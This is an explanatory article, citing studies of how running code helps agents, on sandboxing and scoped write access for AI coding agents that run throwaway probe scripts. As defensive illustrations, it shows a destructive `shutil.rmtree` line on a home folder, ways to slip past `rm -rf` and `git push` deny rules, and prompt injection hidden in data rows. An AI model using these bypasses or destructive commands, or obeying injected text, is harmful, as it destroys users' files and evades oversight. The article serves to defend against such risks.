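# Sandboxing and scoped write access for AI agents that run their own scripts

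## Agents that write and run scripts, and the rights those scripts inherit

A coding agent is a software system in which a language model issues commands to a computer. It reads and edits files, runs tests and uses the results to choose its next step. Many of its commands run small programs that the model has just written. Sandboxing enforces a limit on what these programs can access. One way to do this is scoped write access, which lets the programs run in the user's real environment but create, change or delete files only inside a chosen set of directories, called the write scope. The other way is to run them in a separate environment, such as a container or a virtual machine. People often combine the two.

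Operating systems let a script that an agent starts do whatever the user's account can do, unless something removes some of its rights first. Sandboxing and scoped write access both address this default.

### The agent loop

The model acts on the machine only by requesting tools, which carry out the actions, as the University of Vermont's *Claude Code Permissions & Sandboxing* explains. The program that receives these requests, runs them and returns the results is called the harness. Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex are both harnesses. Anthropic's *How Claude Code works* describes Claude Code as the layer around the model that provides the tools and manages what information the model receives.

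*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes each step of the cycle. The harness combines the user's request, standing instructions and a list of available tools into a prompt for the model. The model returns either a final message or a tool call. A call to the shell tool, which runs terminal commands, contains the command and can also set a working directory and a time limit. The harness runs the command, appends the output to the prompt and queries the model again. This repeats until the model returns a final message, and a single request can lead to hundreds of tool calls.

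Some of those calls run code only to find something out. *Code as Agent Harness* (Fu, Wei and colleagues, 2026), a survey of the field, lists regression tests and temporary tools among the programs that agents create, run, observe and revise during a task. A probe script is a short throwaway program for testing an assumption.

Suppose a user asks an agent why the totals in a monthly report are too low. The project contains an importer that reads CSV files, which are plain-text tables with commas between the columns. After reading the importer's code, the agent suspects that it drops rows with a blank date. It takes 20 sample rows and writes a file, `probe.py`:

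```python
import csv
from importer import load_rows

with open("sample.csv", newline="") as f:
    raw = list(csv.DictReader(f))
kept = load_rows("sample.csv")

print("rows in file:", len(raw))
print("blank dates:", sum(not r["date"].strip() for r in raw))
print("rows kept:", len(kept))
```

It then requests the command `python probe.py`. Suppose the counts are 20, 3 and 17. The harness adds those three lines to the prompt, so the model now has evidence for what had been a guess. The evidence isn't conclusive, because the three missing rows might not be the three with blank dates. A sensible next probe would print which rows are missing.

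### What a script inherits

What else `probe.py` could do depends on how the operating system decides what any program may do. The kernel is the core of the system and directly controls the disk, the memory and the network hardware. An ordinary program can't open a file by itself, so it makes a request to the kernel, known as a system call, which the kernel either carries out or refuses. A running program is called a process, and a process that another one starts is its child. To the kernel, a user account is mostly a number, the user ID. Every process has a user ID, and the kernel compares it with a file's permissions before opening the file.

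On Linux, a child process inherits copies of its parent's user and group IDs, according to the man page *credentials(7)*. The user opens a terminal, which runs under the user's ID. The terminal's shell starts the harness, the harness starts another shell to run the command, and that shell starts Python. If `probe.py` then starts Git, the version-control program, Git also runs under the user's ID. (A few programs, such as `sudo`, change the ID as they start, which is how an ordinary user gets administrator rights.) The kernel's ordinary file check does not depend on whether a person or a model wrote the script.

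A script written to count 20 rows also has the right to empty the user's home directory, read the SSH keys that log the user in to other machines, edit the file that runs whenever a new shell opens, and send data over the network. On an ordinary account it can't replace the operating system's own files, because those belong to the administrator, but the files people most mind losing are usually their own. Wiesen writes in *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows* that Codex runs with a real user's permissions and "can do everything the user can do", which is why it needs a sandbox.

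Inheritance also makes a sandbox workable. If the operating system starts a command with reduced rights, every descendant process inherits those limits. OpenAI's *Sandbox* explains that when Codex runs Git, a package manager or a test runner, those programs inherit the same limits, so nobody has to configure each one.

A script's child processes inherit the sandbox's limits, but a process already running outside the sandbox keeps its own rights. If a script can send requests to that process, it may get the process to do things the script couldn't do itself. Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* gives an example. On WSL2, the Linux layer inside Windows, a command that launches a Windows program hands the job to the Windows host through a socket (a channel between processes), so the sandbox blocks that socket.

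Whether a script's inherited rights are reduced at all depends on the product and its settings. Codex sandboxes commands in its default mode, but Claude Code's sandbox is off until someone turns it on, as the UT Austin course slides *Permissions and sandboxing* warn students.

### A check before the start and a limit during the run

The harness can check a command before it starts, or the operating system can enforce a limit on the process while it runs. The harness can compare the command with a list of rules, show it to the user for approval, or pass it to a classifier that judges whether it looks safe. According to Anthropic, Claude Code decides whether to allow a command based on the command string, with the classifier's judgment added in one mode, whereas the operating system's boundary holds "even if an allowed command does more than its name suggests".

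`python probe.py` is a good example of a command whose name suggests very little. It consists of 15 characters that identify an interpreter and a file. What the process does depends on the contents of the file at the moment it starts, on the importer, on every package the importer loads, and on the data. Add this line to the script (with the two imports it needs) and the command stays the same to the letter:

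```python
shutil.rmtree(Path.home() / "reports")
```

The script now deletes a folder of reports from the user's home directory. A user who reads the file before approving the command will catch that, and reading ten lines of code is worth the half minute. But the harmless-looking line `from importer import load_rows` also runs the importer's own code and that of its packages, which few people will read through. If the user saves a rule that always allows `python probe.py`, the rule matches the text of the command, so it also approves every later version of the file.

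Rules that forbid dangerous commands have the same weakness. In the examples on the UT Austin slides, a rule against commands beginning with `rm -rf`, the usual way to delete a directory tree, doesn't stop `bash -c 'rm -rf …'` or a script that deletes files with a library call. Anthropic acknowledges this weakness in its documentation of permission rules. A rule against `git push` doesn't match `git -C . push`, and the company says that such a rule "isn't a security boundary around the program".

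More careful pattern-writing would close some of these gaps, but not the main one. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* explains that once control passes to a subprocess, the harness can no longer see or control it. Operating-system controls work at a lower level and cover every process in the sandbox, however it started.

OpenAI's first Windows prototype limited network access by setting environment variables that sent web traffic to a dead address, and by placing dummy versions of two remote-access programs ahead of the real ones. These measures changed the environment of the running process, so they went further than checking the command text, but they worked only on programs that respected the settings. Wiesen calls the approach "advisory" because a process could ignore the variables and open a connection directly. The team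 wanted to use a firewall rule instead, but Windows Firewall could not single out the restricted commands while they ran under the user's own account. The current design creates two extra local accounts, blocks outbound traffic for one of them, and runs the agent's commands under these accounts so that they have different rights from the user's.

Harness checks are still necessary when the shell is sandboxed. The University of Vermont points out that the sandbox around shell commands doesn't cover Claude Code's built-in tools for reading and editing files, which run inside the harness process and are governed by permission rules instead. Codex has a similar gap. According to Bolin, its sandbox covers the shell tool that Codex provides, but tools from outside servers must enforce their own limits. Sandboxing the shell therefore restricts `probe.py`, but not everything the agent can do.

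### Where the harm comes from

A script with too many rights does no damage until something goes wrong, and it can go wrong in three ways.

The simplest risk is an honest mistake. Suppose an agent writes a script that calls `load_rows` only to count rows, but overlooks that the function also moves each file it reads into an archive folder, or writes the rows to whatever database the project's settings name. Running the script then changes real data. A cleanup line at the end of a script can do more damage if an empty variable makes its path resolve to the whole project.

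Someone may also attack the agent through prompt injection, by hiding instructions in content that the agent reads and may then follow. NVIDIA treats this as the primary threat to coding agents and lists entry points including malicious repositories, pull requests, Git histories and the instruction files that agents load when they start. In the running example, the probe prints only counts, but the follow-up would print whole rows. If those rows came from customers, a comment field could contain a sentence addressed to the model, which would enter the prompt with the rest of the output. A malicious package doesn't need to go through the prompt. If the agent installs a date-parsing library to compare results, the library's code runs inside the probe's own process, under the user's ID.

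An agent can also pursue its task past what the user intended. For example, a user asks for an explanation of why the totals are low. The agent confirms its guess, repairs the importer, and re-imports last year's files into the live database to correct the totals. Every command does what the agent meant it to do, but the user had asked only for an explanation.

The UT Austin slides describe harness rules on command text as guardrails against accidents. That seems fair, because an agent that blunders will often write the dangerous command in its usual form. An attacker will pick another form, and an agent intent on finishing the job may find one while looking for a way around an obstacle. An operating-system limit works the same way against accidents, attacks and workarounds, but it only restricts where a script can write, whatever the purpose of the write. If the importer's code lies inside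 the write scope, the kernel will allow a script to ruin it.

### Confinement and least privilege

The main ideas date from the 1970s, when the concern was programs written by other people. Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, asked how a customer could run a borrowed program without the program leaking the customer's data to its owner. One of his rules was that any untrusted program called by a confined program must also be confined, which inheritance down the process tree now provides. He also observed that wrong results leave evidence, while a leak generally leaves none. In *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), Saltzer and Schroeder set out the principle of least privilege, which gives every program only the rights its job requires, chiefly to limit the damage from an accident or error. They also advised designers to list what a program may do rather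 than what it may not, because people quickly notice when a program is wrongly blocked but may not notice when it is wrongly allowed to do something.

Applying least privilege requires knowing what a job needs. That's easy for `probe.py`, provided the importer has no side effects. The script must read the importer, its packages and `sample.csv`, and it doesn't need network access or permission to change files. But the agent writes its second script only after seeing the output of the first, and the second might install another CSV library for comparison or save a corrected copy of the sample. Cutting off the network stops a script from sending customer rows to a stranger, but it also stops the installation. Banning all writes protects the importer but also prevents the script from saving the corrected copy. Lampson accepted this kind of loss in 1973, when he didn't require that a program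 that works when free also work when confined.

Before Codex had a Windows sandbox, its Windows users could either approve nearly every command by hand or let everything run unchecked. Wiesen describes how OpenAI looked for a compromise. The team considered AppContainer, Windows' native sandbox, but rejected it because it suits applications whose needs are known in advance, while an agent may run shells, Git, Python, package managers and any other tool the task requires. The default the team chose lets commands read files almost anywhere but write only inside the workspace, the directory where the user started the agent, with no internet access unless the user asks for it. Under those limits, `probe.py` runs unchanged and can't empty the home directory, but it could still overwrite the importer it was written to test.

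## What running code gains an agent, and which rights it takes

To give `probe.py` only the rights it needs, a user can identify most of them by following the script step by step. The benefit of running it is harder to estimate. Agents that fix well-described bugs do almost as well without running code, but agents that analyse data or tune performance can do much worse, so a sensible limit depends on the task.

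### The rights that `probe.py` uses

The agent first creates `probe.py`, and also `sample.csv` if it has to copy the 20 rows out of a larger file. These are its only deliberate writes. The shell then starts Python, which requires the right to execute the interpreter and read Python's standard library. Both usually lie outside the workspace, so a sandbox that let commands read only the project would stop the script before its first line runs.

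The line `from importer import load_rows` makes Python read the importer and every package it loads. Python also compiles these files into a form that loads faster and tries to save the result in a `__pycache__` folder beside the source. A script can therefore write into the project even if its own code never writes a file. If the save fails, Python runs the compiled code from memory, and the script starts slightly slower next time. The script then reads `sample.csv` and prints its three lines.

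Other steps depend on the importer and on what the agent tries next. A package may create temporary files, for example to unpack compressed data. A later probe may start Git or the project's test suite as a child process. Installing another library requires a network connection and write access to Python's package folder.

| Step | Right it uses | Status |
|---|---|---|
| Create `probe.py` and `sample.csv` | Write two small files | Essential, but the files can go outside the project |
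| Start Python | Execute the interpreter, read the standard library | Essential |
| Load the importer | Read the project and its installed packages | Essential |
| Save compiled code | Write to `__pycache__` | Can be redirected or switched off |
| Read the sample | Read one data file | Essential |
| Unpack or buffer data | Write temporary files | Can be redirected |
| Start Git or a test runner | Execute another program | Essential only for some later probes |
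| Install a package | Use the network, write to the package folder | Can be prepared in advance |

`probe.py` needs to read widely but hardly needs to write. The exception would be an importer that also archives the files it reads, because it may stop with an error when it can't write to the archive folder, even though the row count doesn't depend on archiving. Running the probe on a copy of the data avoids granting write access to the real archive.

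A list like this is a guess until someone tests it, and *Aletheia* (Shi, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes a way to do so. An agent runs a task with all the permissions that a project's instruction file asks for, then runs it again from the same starting state with one permission removed. If the result passes the same tests both times, the task didn't need that permission. The method has separate permissions for reading, writing, listing and executing files, running a tool, and connecting to a network address. It also accounts for dependencies, so permission to execute a script includes access to its interpreter.

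Applied to `probe.py`, the method would refuse writes to `__pycache__` and check that the script still prints 20, 3 and 17. It would have to account for overlapping permissions, a problem Shi and colleagues point out. If the whole workspace is writable, withdrawing a separate permission for `__pycache__` doesn't block writes there, so a successful run doesn't show that the permission was unnecessary. Permissions can also substitute for each other. The agent could save its script in the workspace or in a temporary folder, so it can do without either permission but not both. A failed run doesn't prove that the missing permission was essential either, because the agent may have failed for some other reason.

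The system is meant to catch malicious instruction files, which tend to request access the task doesn't need. It flagged all 314 malicious files in the evaluation and 3 of the 85 harmless ones. Checking a file took 44 seconds and cost 22 cents on average. Every trial used the same small job of renaming a Python function, so the low error rate may not carry over to messier work.

*EPISTEME* (2026) provides some evidence on how often agents use the shell to change things. Its system requires a coding agent to declare the purpose of every tool call. In 400 completed runs, two models made 3,714 shell calls and declared 96.3% of them read-only, meaning that their purpose was to collect information, test a hypothesis or verify a result. The models made most of their code changes through the harness's file-editing tools, and when those edits are included, 30% of all calls changed something.

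The labels record only what the models intended, so a test run that an agent declares read-only may still write a cache, and a sandbox that blocks every write would interfere with it. Still, the figures suggest that a user could give shell commands much narrower write access than the editing tools, as long as the commands could write caches and temporary files.

### Fixing bugs with and without running code

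A user could also remove most of these rights by not letting the agent run any code. *To Run or Not to Run* (Lin, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) measures how this affects bug repair on SWE-bench, a collection of real bug reports from open-source Python projects, each with tests to check whether a fix works.

The study began with 7,745 recorded attempts from the benchmark's public leaderboard, covering four harnesses and twelve models. Agents ran tests 8.8 times per task on average, with a range from 2.0 for GPT-5.2 in one harness to 18.7 for Claude Sonnet 4 in another.

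Then they ran an experiment on 200 bugs, half from the Lite selection and half from the Verified selection. Three agents attempted each bug under five conditions, for 3,000 attempts in all. The agents were Claude Code with Claude Sonnet 4.5, Codex with GPT-5.2, and the open-source OpenCode with a much weaker model, Qwen2.5-Coder-32B. In the strictest condition, the prompt told the agent not to run tests or project scripts, and the project's required packages were missing. Two conditions gave the agent a budget of one or three test runs, and another only reminded it that runs cost money. In the last, the agent could run anything.

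| Agent and bug set (100 bugs each) | Solved without execution | Solved with free execution | Solved only without | Solved only with |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, Lite | 63 | 64 | 5 | 6 |
| Claude Code, Verified | 64 | 67 | 6 | 9 |
| Codex, Lite | 74 | 73 | 4 | 3 |
| Codex, Verified | 73 | 75 | 1 | 3 |
| OpenCode, Lite | 7 | 6 | 4 | 3 |
| OpenCode, Verified | 13 | 14 | 4 | 5 |

Free execution raised the two commercial agents' success rate by an average of 1.25 percentage points. Claude Code sometimes tried to run tests despite the prompt, so Lin and colleagues repeated its Verified runs with the harness blocking test commands. With those commands blocked, it solved 63%, compared with 67% with free execution.

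The ban also saved money. Claude Code used 56–62% fewer tokens (the word fragments by which providers bill text) and finished in about half the time. Codex used only 1–14% fewer tokens.

The runs helped so little partly because the agents could usually find the right file without them. On bugs that a commercial agent solved both with and without the ability to run code, it edited a correct file in more than 95% of cases under either condition. The agents' own checks also missed many failures because they tested something other than what the official tests covered. Among the failed repairs that the commercial agents had tested after editing, 81% for Claude Code and 100% for Codex had passed at least one of the agent's own checks.

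With the weak model, OpenCode did best when limited to one test run, solving 14 and 17 bugs on the two sets. It solved fewer when it could run code freely. Lin and colleagues attribute this drop to test output crowding the model's limited context, the amount of text it can take in at once.

These results don't quite show that agents can fix bugs as well by reading code as by running it. None of the differences is statistically significant, but with 100 bugs per comparison, a real difference could easily go undetected. Lin and colleagues formally tested for equivalence with a margin of five points, and only one of the six comparisons passed. For Claude Code on Verified, a standard paired calculation from the table's counts puts the effect of free execution between about 5 points worse and 11 points better. Pooling the four commercial comparisons narrows this range to between 2 points worse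 and 4 better, although it treats two agents' attempts at the same bug as independent. A large average benefit on these bugs is therefore unlikely, but a moderate benefit for one agent is quite possible.

The bugs and their fixes are also public, so a model that saw them in training may not need to run code. Lin and colleagues checked for this by comparing the patches from the two extreme conditions, and found identical ones in only 24% of cases for Claude Code and 1% for Codex. That makes word-for-word recall an unlikely explanation, but a model can know a project well without reproducing a patch exactly. Lin and colleagues also point out that Qwen2.5-Coder-32B's training data predates Verified. That data could still include the fixes, because Verified was selected from an older set of issues already resolved on GitHub.

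Newer models have replaced the ones in the experiment, and it isn't clear whether they would gain more or less from running code. A better model may work out more by reading, or it may design better probes and learn more from each.

The main caveat for setting limits is that the ban covered running code but not editing files. An agent under the strictest condition could still change files with its editing tools, search the repository and use a plain Python interpreter for small calculations. None of the five conditions restricted where a command could write. The experiment therefore measures the effect of losing nearly all project runs. A write scope that allows most runs should reduce exploration less, unless the agent wastes a lot of time on the few that fail.

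### Looking at values and checking them

A second study, *Rethinking the Value of Agent-Generated Tests for LLM-Based Software Engineering Agents* (Chen, Peng and colleagues, 2026), examined the test files that agents wrote for themselves in 5,000 runs on the 500 bugs of SWE-bench Verified. It used a simple harness that let the model decide whether to test. Claude Opus 4.5 wrote test files in 83.6% of tasks and solved 74.4% of the bugs. GPT-5.2 wrote them in 2.4% of tasks and solved 71.8%. Kimi K2 Thinking wrote them in almost every task and solved 63.4%.

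Models differ in many ways besides their use of test files, so Chen and colleagues measured the effect of those files by changing the instructions given to four models. When asked to write tests, GPT-5.2 solved 359 bugs, the same number as before, though 27 of them were different bugs. It also produced 20% more output tokens. When asked not to write new test files, Kimi K2 Thinking used about half as many input tokens and solved 304 bugs instead of 317. DeepSeek v3.2 Reasoner used a third fewer input tokens and solved 291 bugs instead of 300.

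Neither drop is statistically significant. But the margin of error for Kimi runs from a loss of 6.4 points to a gain of 1.2, and Chen and colleagues say their comparisons do not establish equivalent effectiveness. Small differences in software version between the old and new runs add some uncertainty.

An agent that writes no test files may still run code. The study counted Python files whose names start with `test` or end in `_test.py` or `tests.py`, so it would miss a file named `probe.py`. Agents in the no-test group could also run the project's existing tests or type a few lines of Python into the shell. GPT-5.2 evidently does run code, since it averaged two test runs per task with a harness of the same family in the leaderboard traces that Lin and colleagues analysed.

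Conventional tests contain assertions, which stop the program with an error if a condition is false. Agents' test files contained far more statements that print values from the running program than assertions. In the tasks that Claude Opus 4.5 solved, its test files contained about 20 prints and 5 assertions on average. All five models with enough files to compare used more prints than assertions. More than 70% of the prints displayed results, intermediate values or the contents of objects.

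This suggests that agents write test files to inspect a program as much as to verify it. The two uses aren't easy to separate by counting statements, because an agent can check a result without an assertion by printing a number and comparing it with what it expected. For example, `probe.py` has three print statements, and the agent notices that 20 minus 3 is 17. For either use, there is little reason to give a script write access to the project if it only reads the project and prints values.

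### Work that depends on seeing the output

SWE-bench bugs suit an agent that can only read files, because each bug comes with a description of the problem and its cause is in source code the agent can open. Other tasks depend on facts that no file contains, such as how long a request takes under load.

*Is Your Long-Horizon Benchmark Really Deep?* (Huang, Hua and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes the work in a terminal task, meaning the number of operations, from its depth. Depth is the number of turns that must happen in sequence because the agent has to read the output of one turn before it can choose the commands for the next. More exactly, it is the smallest number of turns that is enough regardless of details the agent doesn't know in advance, such as a file's contents or a program's version. A script that handles all the likely cases itself doesn't add depth. The agent investigating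 the importer could have saved a turn by printing the missing rows along with the counts.

Huang and colleagues estimate a task's depth by finding the smallest turn limit at which either of two models solves it. They tell the agent the limit and stop it there. In four existing sets of automatically generated tasks, 94% of the tasks that a model could solve needed at most three turns. Tasks written by people did not look much deeper. In many cases the agent could issue every command at the start without reading any output.

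They then built 105 tasks around real software, each with steps where the usual method fails and an agent can find this out only by running the commands. One model solved 54 of the tasks, with a median depth of 40 turns, and the best of six models passed 47% of its attempts. The results show that some work can't be planned in advance, and that an agent can run dozens of rounds of experiments without network access if the software is already installed. They don't show how common such work is, because the tasks were designed to take many turns.

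Performance tuning also depends on measurement. In *Benchmarking Coding Agents for System-Level Performance Optimization*, Zhang, Guan and colleagues (2026) planted performance faults in applications made of many cooperating services and asked agents to remove them. In almost half of the attempts that scored zero, the agent had written correct code that made nothing faster. One agent read the code containing the main fault, a lock that forced requests to wait for each other, and decided the operations inside it were "cheap". It left the lock unchanged, and the average request still took almost six seconds.

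Zhang and colleagues then gave Claude Code, running the Qwen3.7-Max model, a tool that measures where an application spends its time. Its score rose from 39.4 to 47.7 out of 100, where 100 means the agent recovered all of the lost speed. This was a single run, and results got worse on two of the seven applications. The agents without the tool could already run a load test, so the gain comes from better measurements and the encouragement to use them. In one case, the tool measured a delay of 22.2 seconds on one path and 10.8 milliseconds on the alternative, which answered a question the agent had twice got wrong by reading.

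*PerfAgent* (2026) reports a similar change in behaviour. Its agent, which had timing data, modified low-level code on 48% of tasks, compared with 31% for an agent without that data. It also did better on the tasks that called for such changes.

*NetAgent* (2026) tests a choice close to the one facing someone who sandboxes scripts. Its system looks for attacks in records of network traffic, normally by writing its own code. When it could only call functions from the same library one at a time, and couldn't combine them in a script, its F1 score, which combines missed attacks and false alarms, fell by 26.57 points. The result covers one data-analysis task, but it suggests that an agent limited to approved operations can perform much worse than one that can write any code it likes in a sandbox.

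*ReCodeAgent* (Ibrahimzada, Kroening and colleagues, 2026) uses separate agents to translate whole projects from one programming language to another. Removing the agent that runs the translated tests and diagnoses failures cut the test pass rate by 30.3%. That agent also writes extra tests, and removing the planning agent lowered the pass rate nearly as much, so only part of the drop can come from not running the code.

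Machine-learning experiments give the clearest evidence of how well a model can predict results without running code. In *Can LLMs predict the outcomes of machine learning experiments?*, Bansal, Pareja and colleagues (2026) collected 288 ideas for changing a machine-learning program, ran them, and asked five current models to predict each new score. The best model, Claude Opus 5.5, predicted the direction of the change correctly for 82% of the ideas, but its predictions accounted for only about half of the variation in the real outcomes (R² = 0.49). All five models underestimated the size of the changes. According to a simple statistical model, an agent that ran only the idea Opus 5.5 ranked highest could expect about 70% of the gain from the best idea.

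An agent can use prediction to decide which experiments to run first. In *AI Research Preference Models* (Foster, Al Omari and colleagues, 2026), a research agent proposed up to 15 candidate programs at each step and ran only one. Choosing at random gave an average score of 0.684 over 20 tasks, where 1 matches the best published result. Reasoning about the candidates raised the score to 0.711, and adding small pilot runs before the choice raised it to 0.729. The pilots added less than reasoning did, but they still helped with their own computing time counted. The pilots ran in a sandbox with the necessary Python packages already installed.

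Some results favour prediction more strongly. In *Can We Predict Before Executing Machine Learning Agents?*, Zheng, Zhang and colleagues (2026) built an agent that predicts which of its solutions will do better before it runs any. It reached good solutions six times faster than agents that relied on execution alone, and finished 6% ahead of them. *MLE-World* (2026) goes further and predicts what a program would print, running the program only when the prediction is too uncertain. Both systems run fewer experiments but still run code in the cases that matter.

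In *Identical Runs, Different Results* (2026), attempts by the same agent and model tended to score higher when they used more of their computing budget, with a rank correlation of 0.55 over 312 attempts. This suggests that more runs may help, but the extra computing needn't have caused the higher scores, because an agent may keep going when its search is going well.

The evidence supports cutting routine test runs in ordinary bug repair if cost matters, but not a general ban. The value of a run depends on how uncertain the agent is about the output and whether that output would change its next step.

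### When a limit pays for itself

A user can weigh these gains against the risk with a simple inequality. A limit pays when

**expected damage prevented > value of the runs blocked + overhead**

The expected damage is the chance of each kind of accident multiplied by the harm it would do, and the limit's benefit is only the part of that damage it prevents. The value of a blocked run is what the user loses by not having it. If the agent can get the same answer by writing to a temporary folder, the user loses only the extra time that takes. Overhead includes the time to set up the limit, interruptions to the user and any delay in starting each command.

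Start-up delay often adds little to the total time spent on tools. In the coding sessions that *TraceLab* (2026) analyses, the average tool call takes 16.8 seconds, so half a second of extra delay per call would add about 3%. The delay would be much more noticeable on short commands, which are the most common. For Claude, 70% of calls finish in under a second.

The numbers in this example are invented. An agent runs 2,000 commands a month for one user. Without limits, one command in 20,000 destroys files outside the project, or an average of 0.1 accidents a month. Each accident takes 30 hours to repair, so the expected loss is 3 hours a month. Limiting writes to the workspace would prevent 90% of that loss, or 2.7 hours a month.

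The same limit blocks 1% of the commands, or 20 a month. The user spends three minutes getting each answer another way, which adds up to an hour a month. Maintaining the limit takes another half hour.

2.7 hours > 1 hour + 0.5 hours

The write scope saves the user 1.2 hours a month. If it blocked 3% of the commands, the time lost to it would rise to 3.5 hours, and the limit would no longer be worthwhile. The user would then do better to check which writes it was blocking before removing it. If most of them were to caches and temporary files, redirecting these into the write scope would let the commands run without exposing anything else.

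The accident rate is the hardest number to estimate, and the damage from an accident varies enormously. Someone without backups might lose months of work, which would justify the write scope even if accidents were ten times rarer. The value of blocked runs depends on the task. For an agent that mostly fixes well-described bugs, the results of Lin and colleagues suggest a low value per run, and for Claude Code a ban on execution even saved tokens. But such a ban prevents only the damage that comes from running code, since the editing tools can still overwrite the importer.

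Each additional limit also needs its own comparison, because it can prevent only the damage that the existing limits still allow. In the invented example, the write scope leaves an expected loss of 0.3 hours, or 18 minutes, a month from destroyed files. A second limit against the same accidents would be worth adding only if it took less of the user's time than that. A limit on network access would need a separate calculation, because it prevents a different kind of damage.

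## Temporary folders and disposable copies of a project

A write scope that covers the whole workspace still lets `probe.py` overwrite the importer. To protect the project too, the user can have the agent experiment in a temporary folder or on a disposable copy of the project.

Running a script in a temporary folder or a disposable copy of a project does not by itself restrict the script. A script that starts in a temporary folder can still change a file in the home directory by using its full path. Protecting the original files also requires a write scope that excludes them.

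### Temporary directories

On Linux, `/tmp` holds short-lived files for every program on the machine. Saving `probe.py` and `sample.csv` there keeps them out of the project, but other programs can write to the same paths. If two agents both write `/tmp/sample.csv`, one may count the other's 20 rows instead of its own.

Cleaning up a shared folder is also risky. Red Hat notes that services, applications and users all keep files in `/tmp`, and experienced administrators advise against removing a file unless you know nothing is using it. Linux normally stops users from deleting each other's files there, but this doesn't protect the user's other programs from an agent, because the agent runs under the same account. Codex lets sandboxed commands write to `/tmp` unless the user excludes it with a setting described in OpenAI's *Configuration Reference*.

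A private directory for each session avoids most of these collisions. The command `mktemp -d` creates a folder with a unique name that only the user's account can open. Most programs put their temporary files there if the variable `TMPDIR` contains its path. To run the probe this way, the agent saves `probe.py` and a copy of the sample in the new folder, here called `$dir`, and enters:

```sh
cd "$dir"
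TMPDIR="$dir" PYTHONPATH=/path/to/project \
PYTHONPYCACHEPREFIX="$dir/cache" python probe.py
```

Python uses `PYTHONPATH` to find the importer, since the script is no longer in the same folder. `PYTHONPYCACHEPREFIX` sends the compiled code to the temporary folder instead of the project's `__pycache__`. If the importer moves each file it reads into an archive, it now moves the copy of the sample, but it may still put that copy in the real archive unless the write scope blocks it.

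Some programs ignore `TMPDIR` and always use `/tmp`. In *Sandlock*, Wang and Zheng (2026) ran Python, Node and other common tools inside their sandbox, and the main adjustment was to grant each tool access to its temporary directories. A stricter setup gives the agent's processes an empty private folder at `/tmp`, so even programs that ignore `TMPDIR` can't touch the shared one.

The user or harness cleans up by deleting the session's folder after the session ends. It is harder to tell whether a session has ended if someone leaves an agent open in a terminal for a week.

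An in-memory file system doesn't need a deletion script, because its files disappear when the user unmounts it or restarts the machine. On Linux its default size limit is half the machine's memory, so a runaway probe can't fill the disk, though it can take memory that other programs need. Linux may move some of the contents to disk when memory runs short, so this isn't a safe place for secrets.

All these folders do only one thing for a project, which is to keep stray files out of it. That is enough for a script that reads the importer and prints three numbers, but an agent testing a repair needs a copy of the project that it can change.

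### Worktrees and full copies

A Git worktree is a second working directory for the same repository. It has its own files, so an agent can edit `importer.py` there without changing the user's copy. Git fills it only with tracked files, those the user has told Git to record. Conductor, a program for running several agents in parallel, can therefore copy chosen ignored files into each new worktree and run a setup script that installs packages or prepares a database.

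A worktree may also start from the wrong version of the code. By default, Claude Code bases new worktrees on the main branch of the remote repository, according to Anthropic. If the user has changed the importer but hasn't pushed the change, a probe in the worktree will test the old importer. A setting makes Claude Code start from the latest local commit instead. Codex can also carry over uncommitted edits if the user starts from the branch that contains them, according to OpenAI's *Worktrees*.

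The separation is only partial. All worktrees share one `.git` folder, which holds the repository's history, so a damaging Git command in one can affect the others. During a worktree session, Claude Code blocks file edits aimed at the main checkout (the user's original working directory). But it doesn't track which files a shell command writes, so its worktree checks won't stop a `cp` command that overwrites the real importer. On most systems, if the user chooses to always allow `python probe.py` in a worktree, Claude Code also applies that rule in the main checkout and keeps it after the worktree is gone.

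A full copy of the project folder includes uncommitted edits, ignored files and any packages stored inside the project. It also has its own Git history. It takes more time and disk space, and it duplicates any passwords in settings files. Those files can also contain full paths to the original folder, and a copied database address still points to the live database.

| What the experiment needs | Git worktree | Full copy | Copy-on-write layer |
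|---|---|---|---|
| Tracked source files | Separate copy | Separate copy | Separate view |
| Uncommitted edits | Depends on the tool | Included | Included |
| Ignored files, such as local settings | Only if someone copies them | Included | Included |
| Packages inside the project folder | Usually reinstalled | Included, but may refer to old paths | Included |
| Git history | Shared with the original | Separate copy | Separate view |
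| Database on a server | Shared | Shared | Shared |

Harnesses usually remove worktrees themselves. When an interactive session ends, Claude Code checks for changed or untracked files and new commits, and asks before it deletes any. Codex keeps the 15 most recent worktrees by default and saves a snapshot before it deletes one.

A snapshot may not contain everything. According to *managed worktrees*, OpenClaw, another agent program, takes a snapshot of tracked and untracked files before a worktree is removed, but leaves out files that Git ignores. If a probe wrote its results to an ignored folder, they would be lost. Full copies have no such safeguard, because the user or the agent just deletes the folder.

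### Copy-on-write with BranchFS

A copy-on-write layer lets a script see the whole project without copying it first. The script can edit and delete files as usual, but the layer stores its changes separately until someone accepts them.

*Fork, Explore, Commit* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) presents BranchFS, a file system of this kind for agents on Linux. It runs as an ordinary program, so the user doesn't need administrator rights.

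The agent first creates a branch, and BranchFS makes an empty directory for the branch's changes. Creation took 292 microseconds for a project of 100 files, 310 microseconds for one of 10,000, and under 350 microseconds in every test, so project size makes almost no difference. The original is read-only within BranchFS while branches exist, so it can't change during an experiment.

The agent then runs its script in the branch. The first time the script changes a file, BranchFS copies the whole file into the branch's directory, and later reads and writes use that copy. The script still reads unchanged files from the original. If the script deletes a file, BranchFS leaves the original in place and records a deletion marker, so the file looks deleted only inside the branch. Copying whole files is simple and works well for source code, but changing one line of a 2 GB data file means copying 2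 GB.

Finally, the agent commits or discards the branch. A commit applies the branch's deletions to the original, then copies the changed files into it. Committing 1 KB of changes took 317 microseconds, 100 KB took 514 microseconds, and 1 MB took 2.1 milliseconds. Discarding the same amounts took between 315 and 890 microseconds.

These times are medians of ten trials on one modest machine, and they exclude the time needed to start the BranchFS command. The slowdown is more noticeable when reading files. In its ordinary mode, BranchFS read a large file at 19% of the disk's normal speed. A faster mode, which bypasses the BranchFS program for unchanged files, reached 82%. Either mode is probably fast enough for an agent that waits up to ten seconds for each reply from the model.

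Suppose a follow-up probe confirms that the three missing rows are the ones with blank dates. The agent then writes three versions of `probe.py`, each of which applies a different repair to the importer and recounts the rows. All three run at the same time in separate branches.

| Branch | Repair | Changes in the branch | Rows kept | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A | Keep rows with a blank date | `importer.py` edited | 20 | Finishes first and commits |
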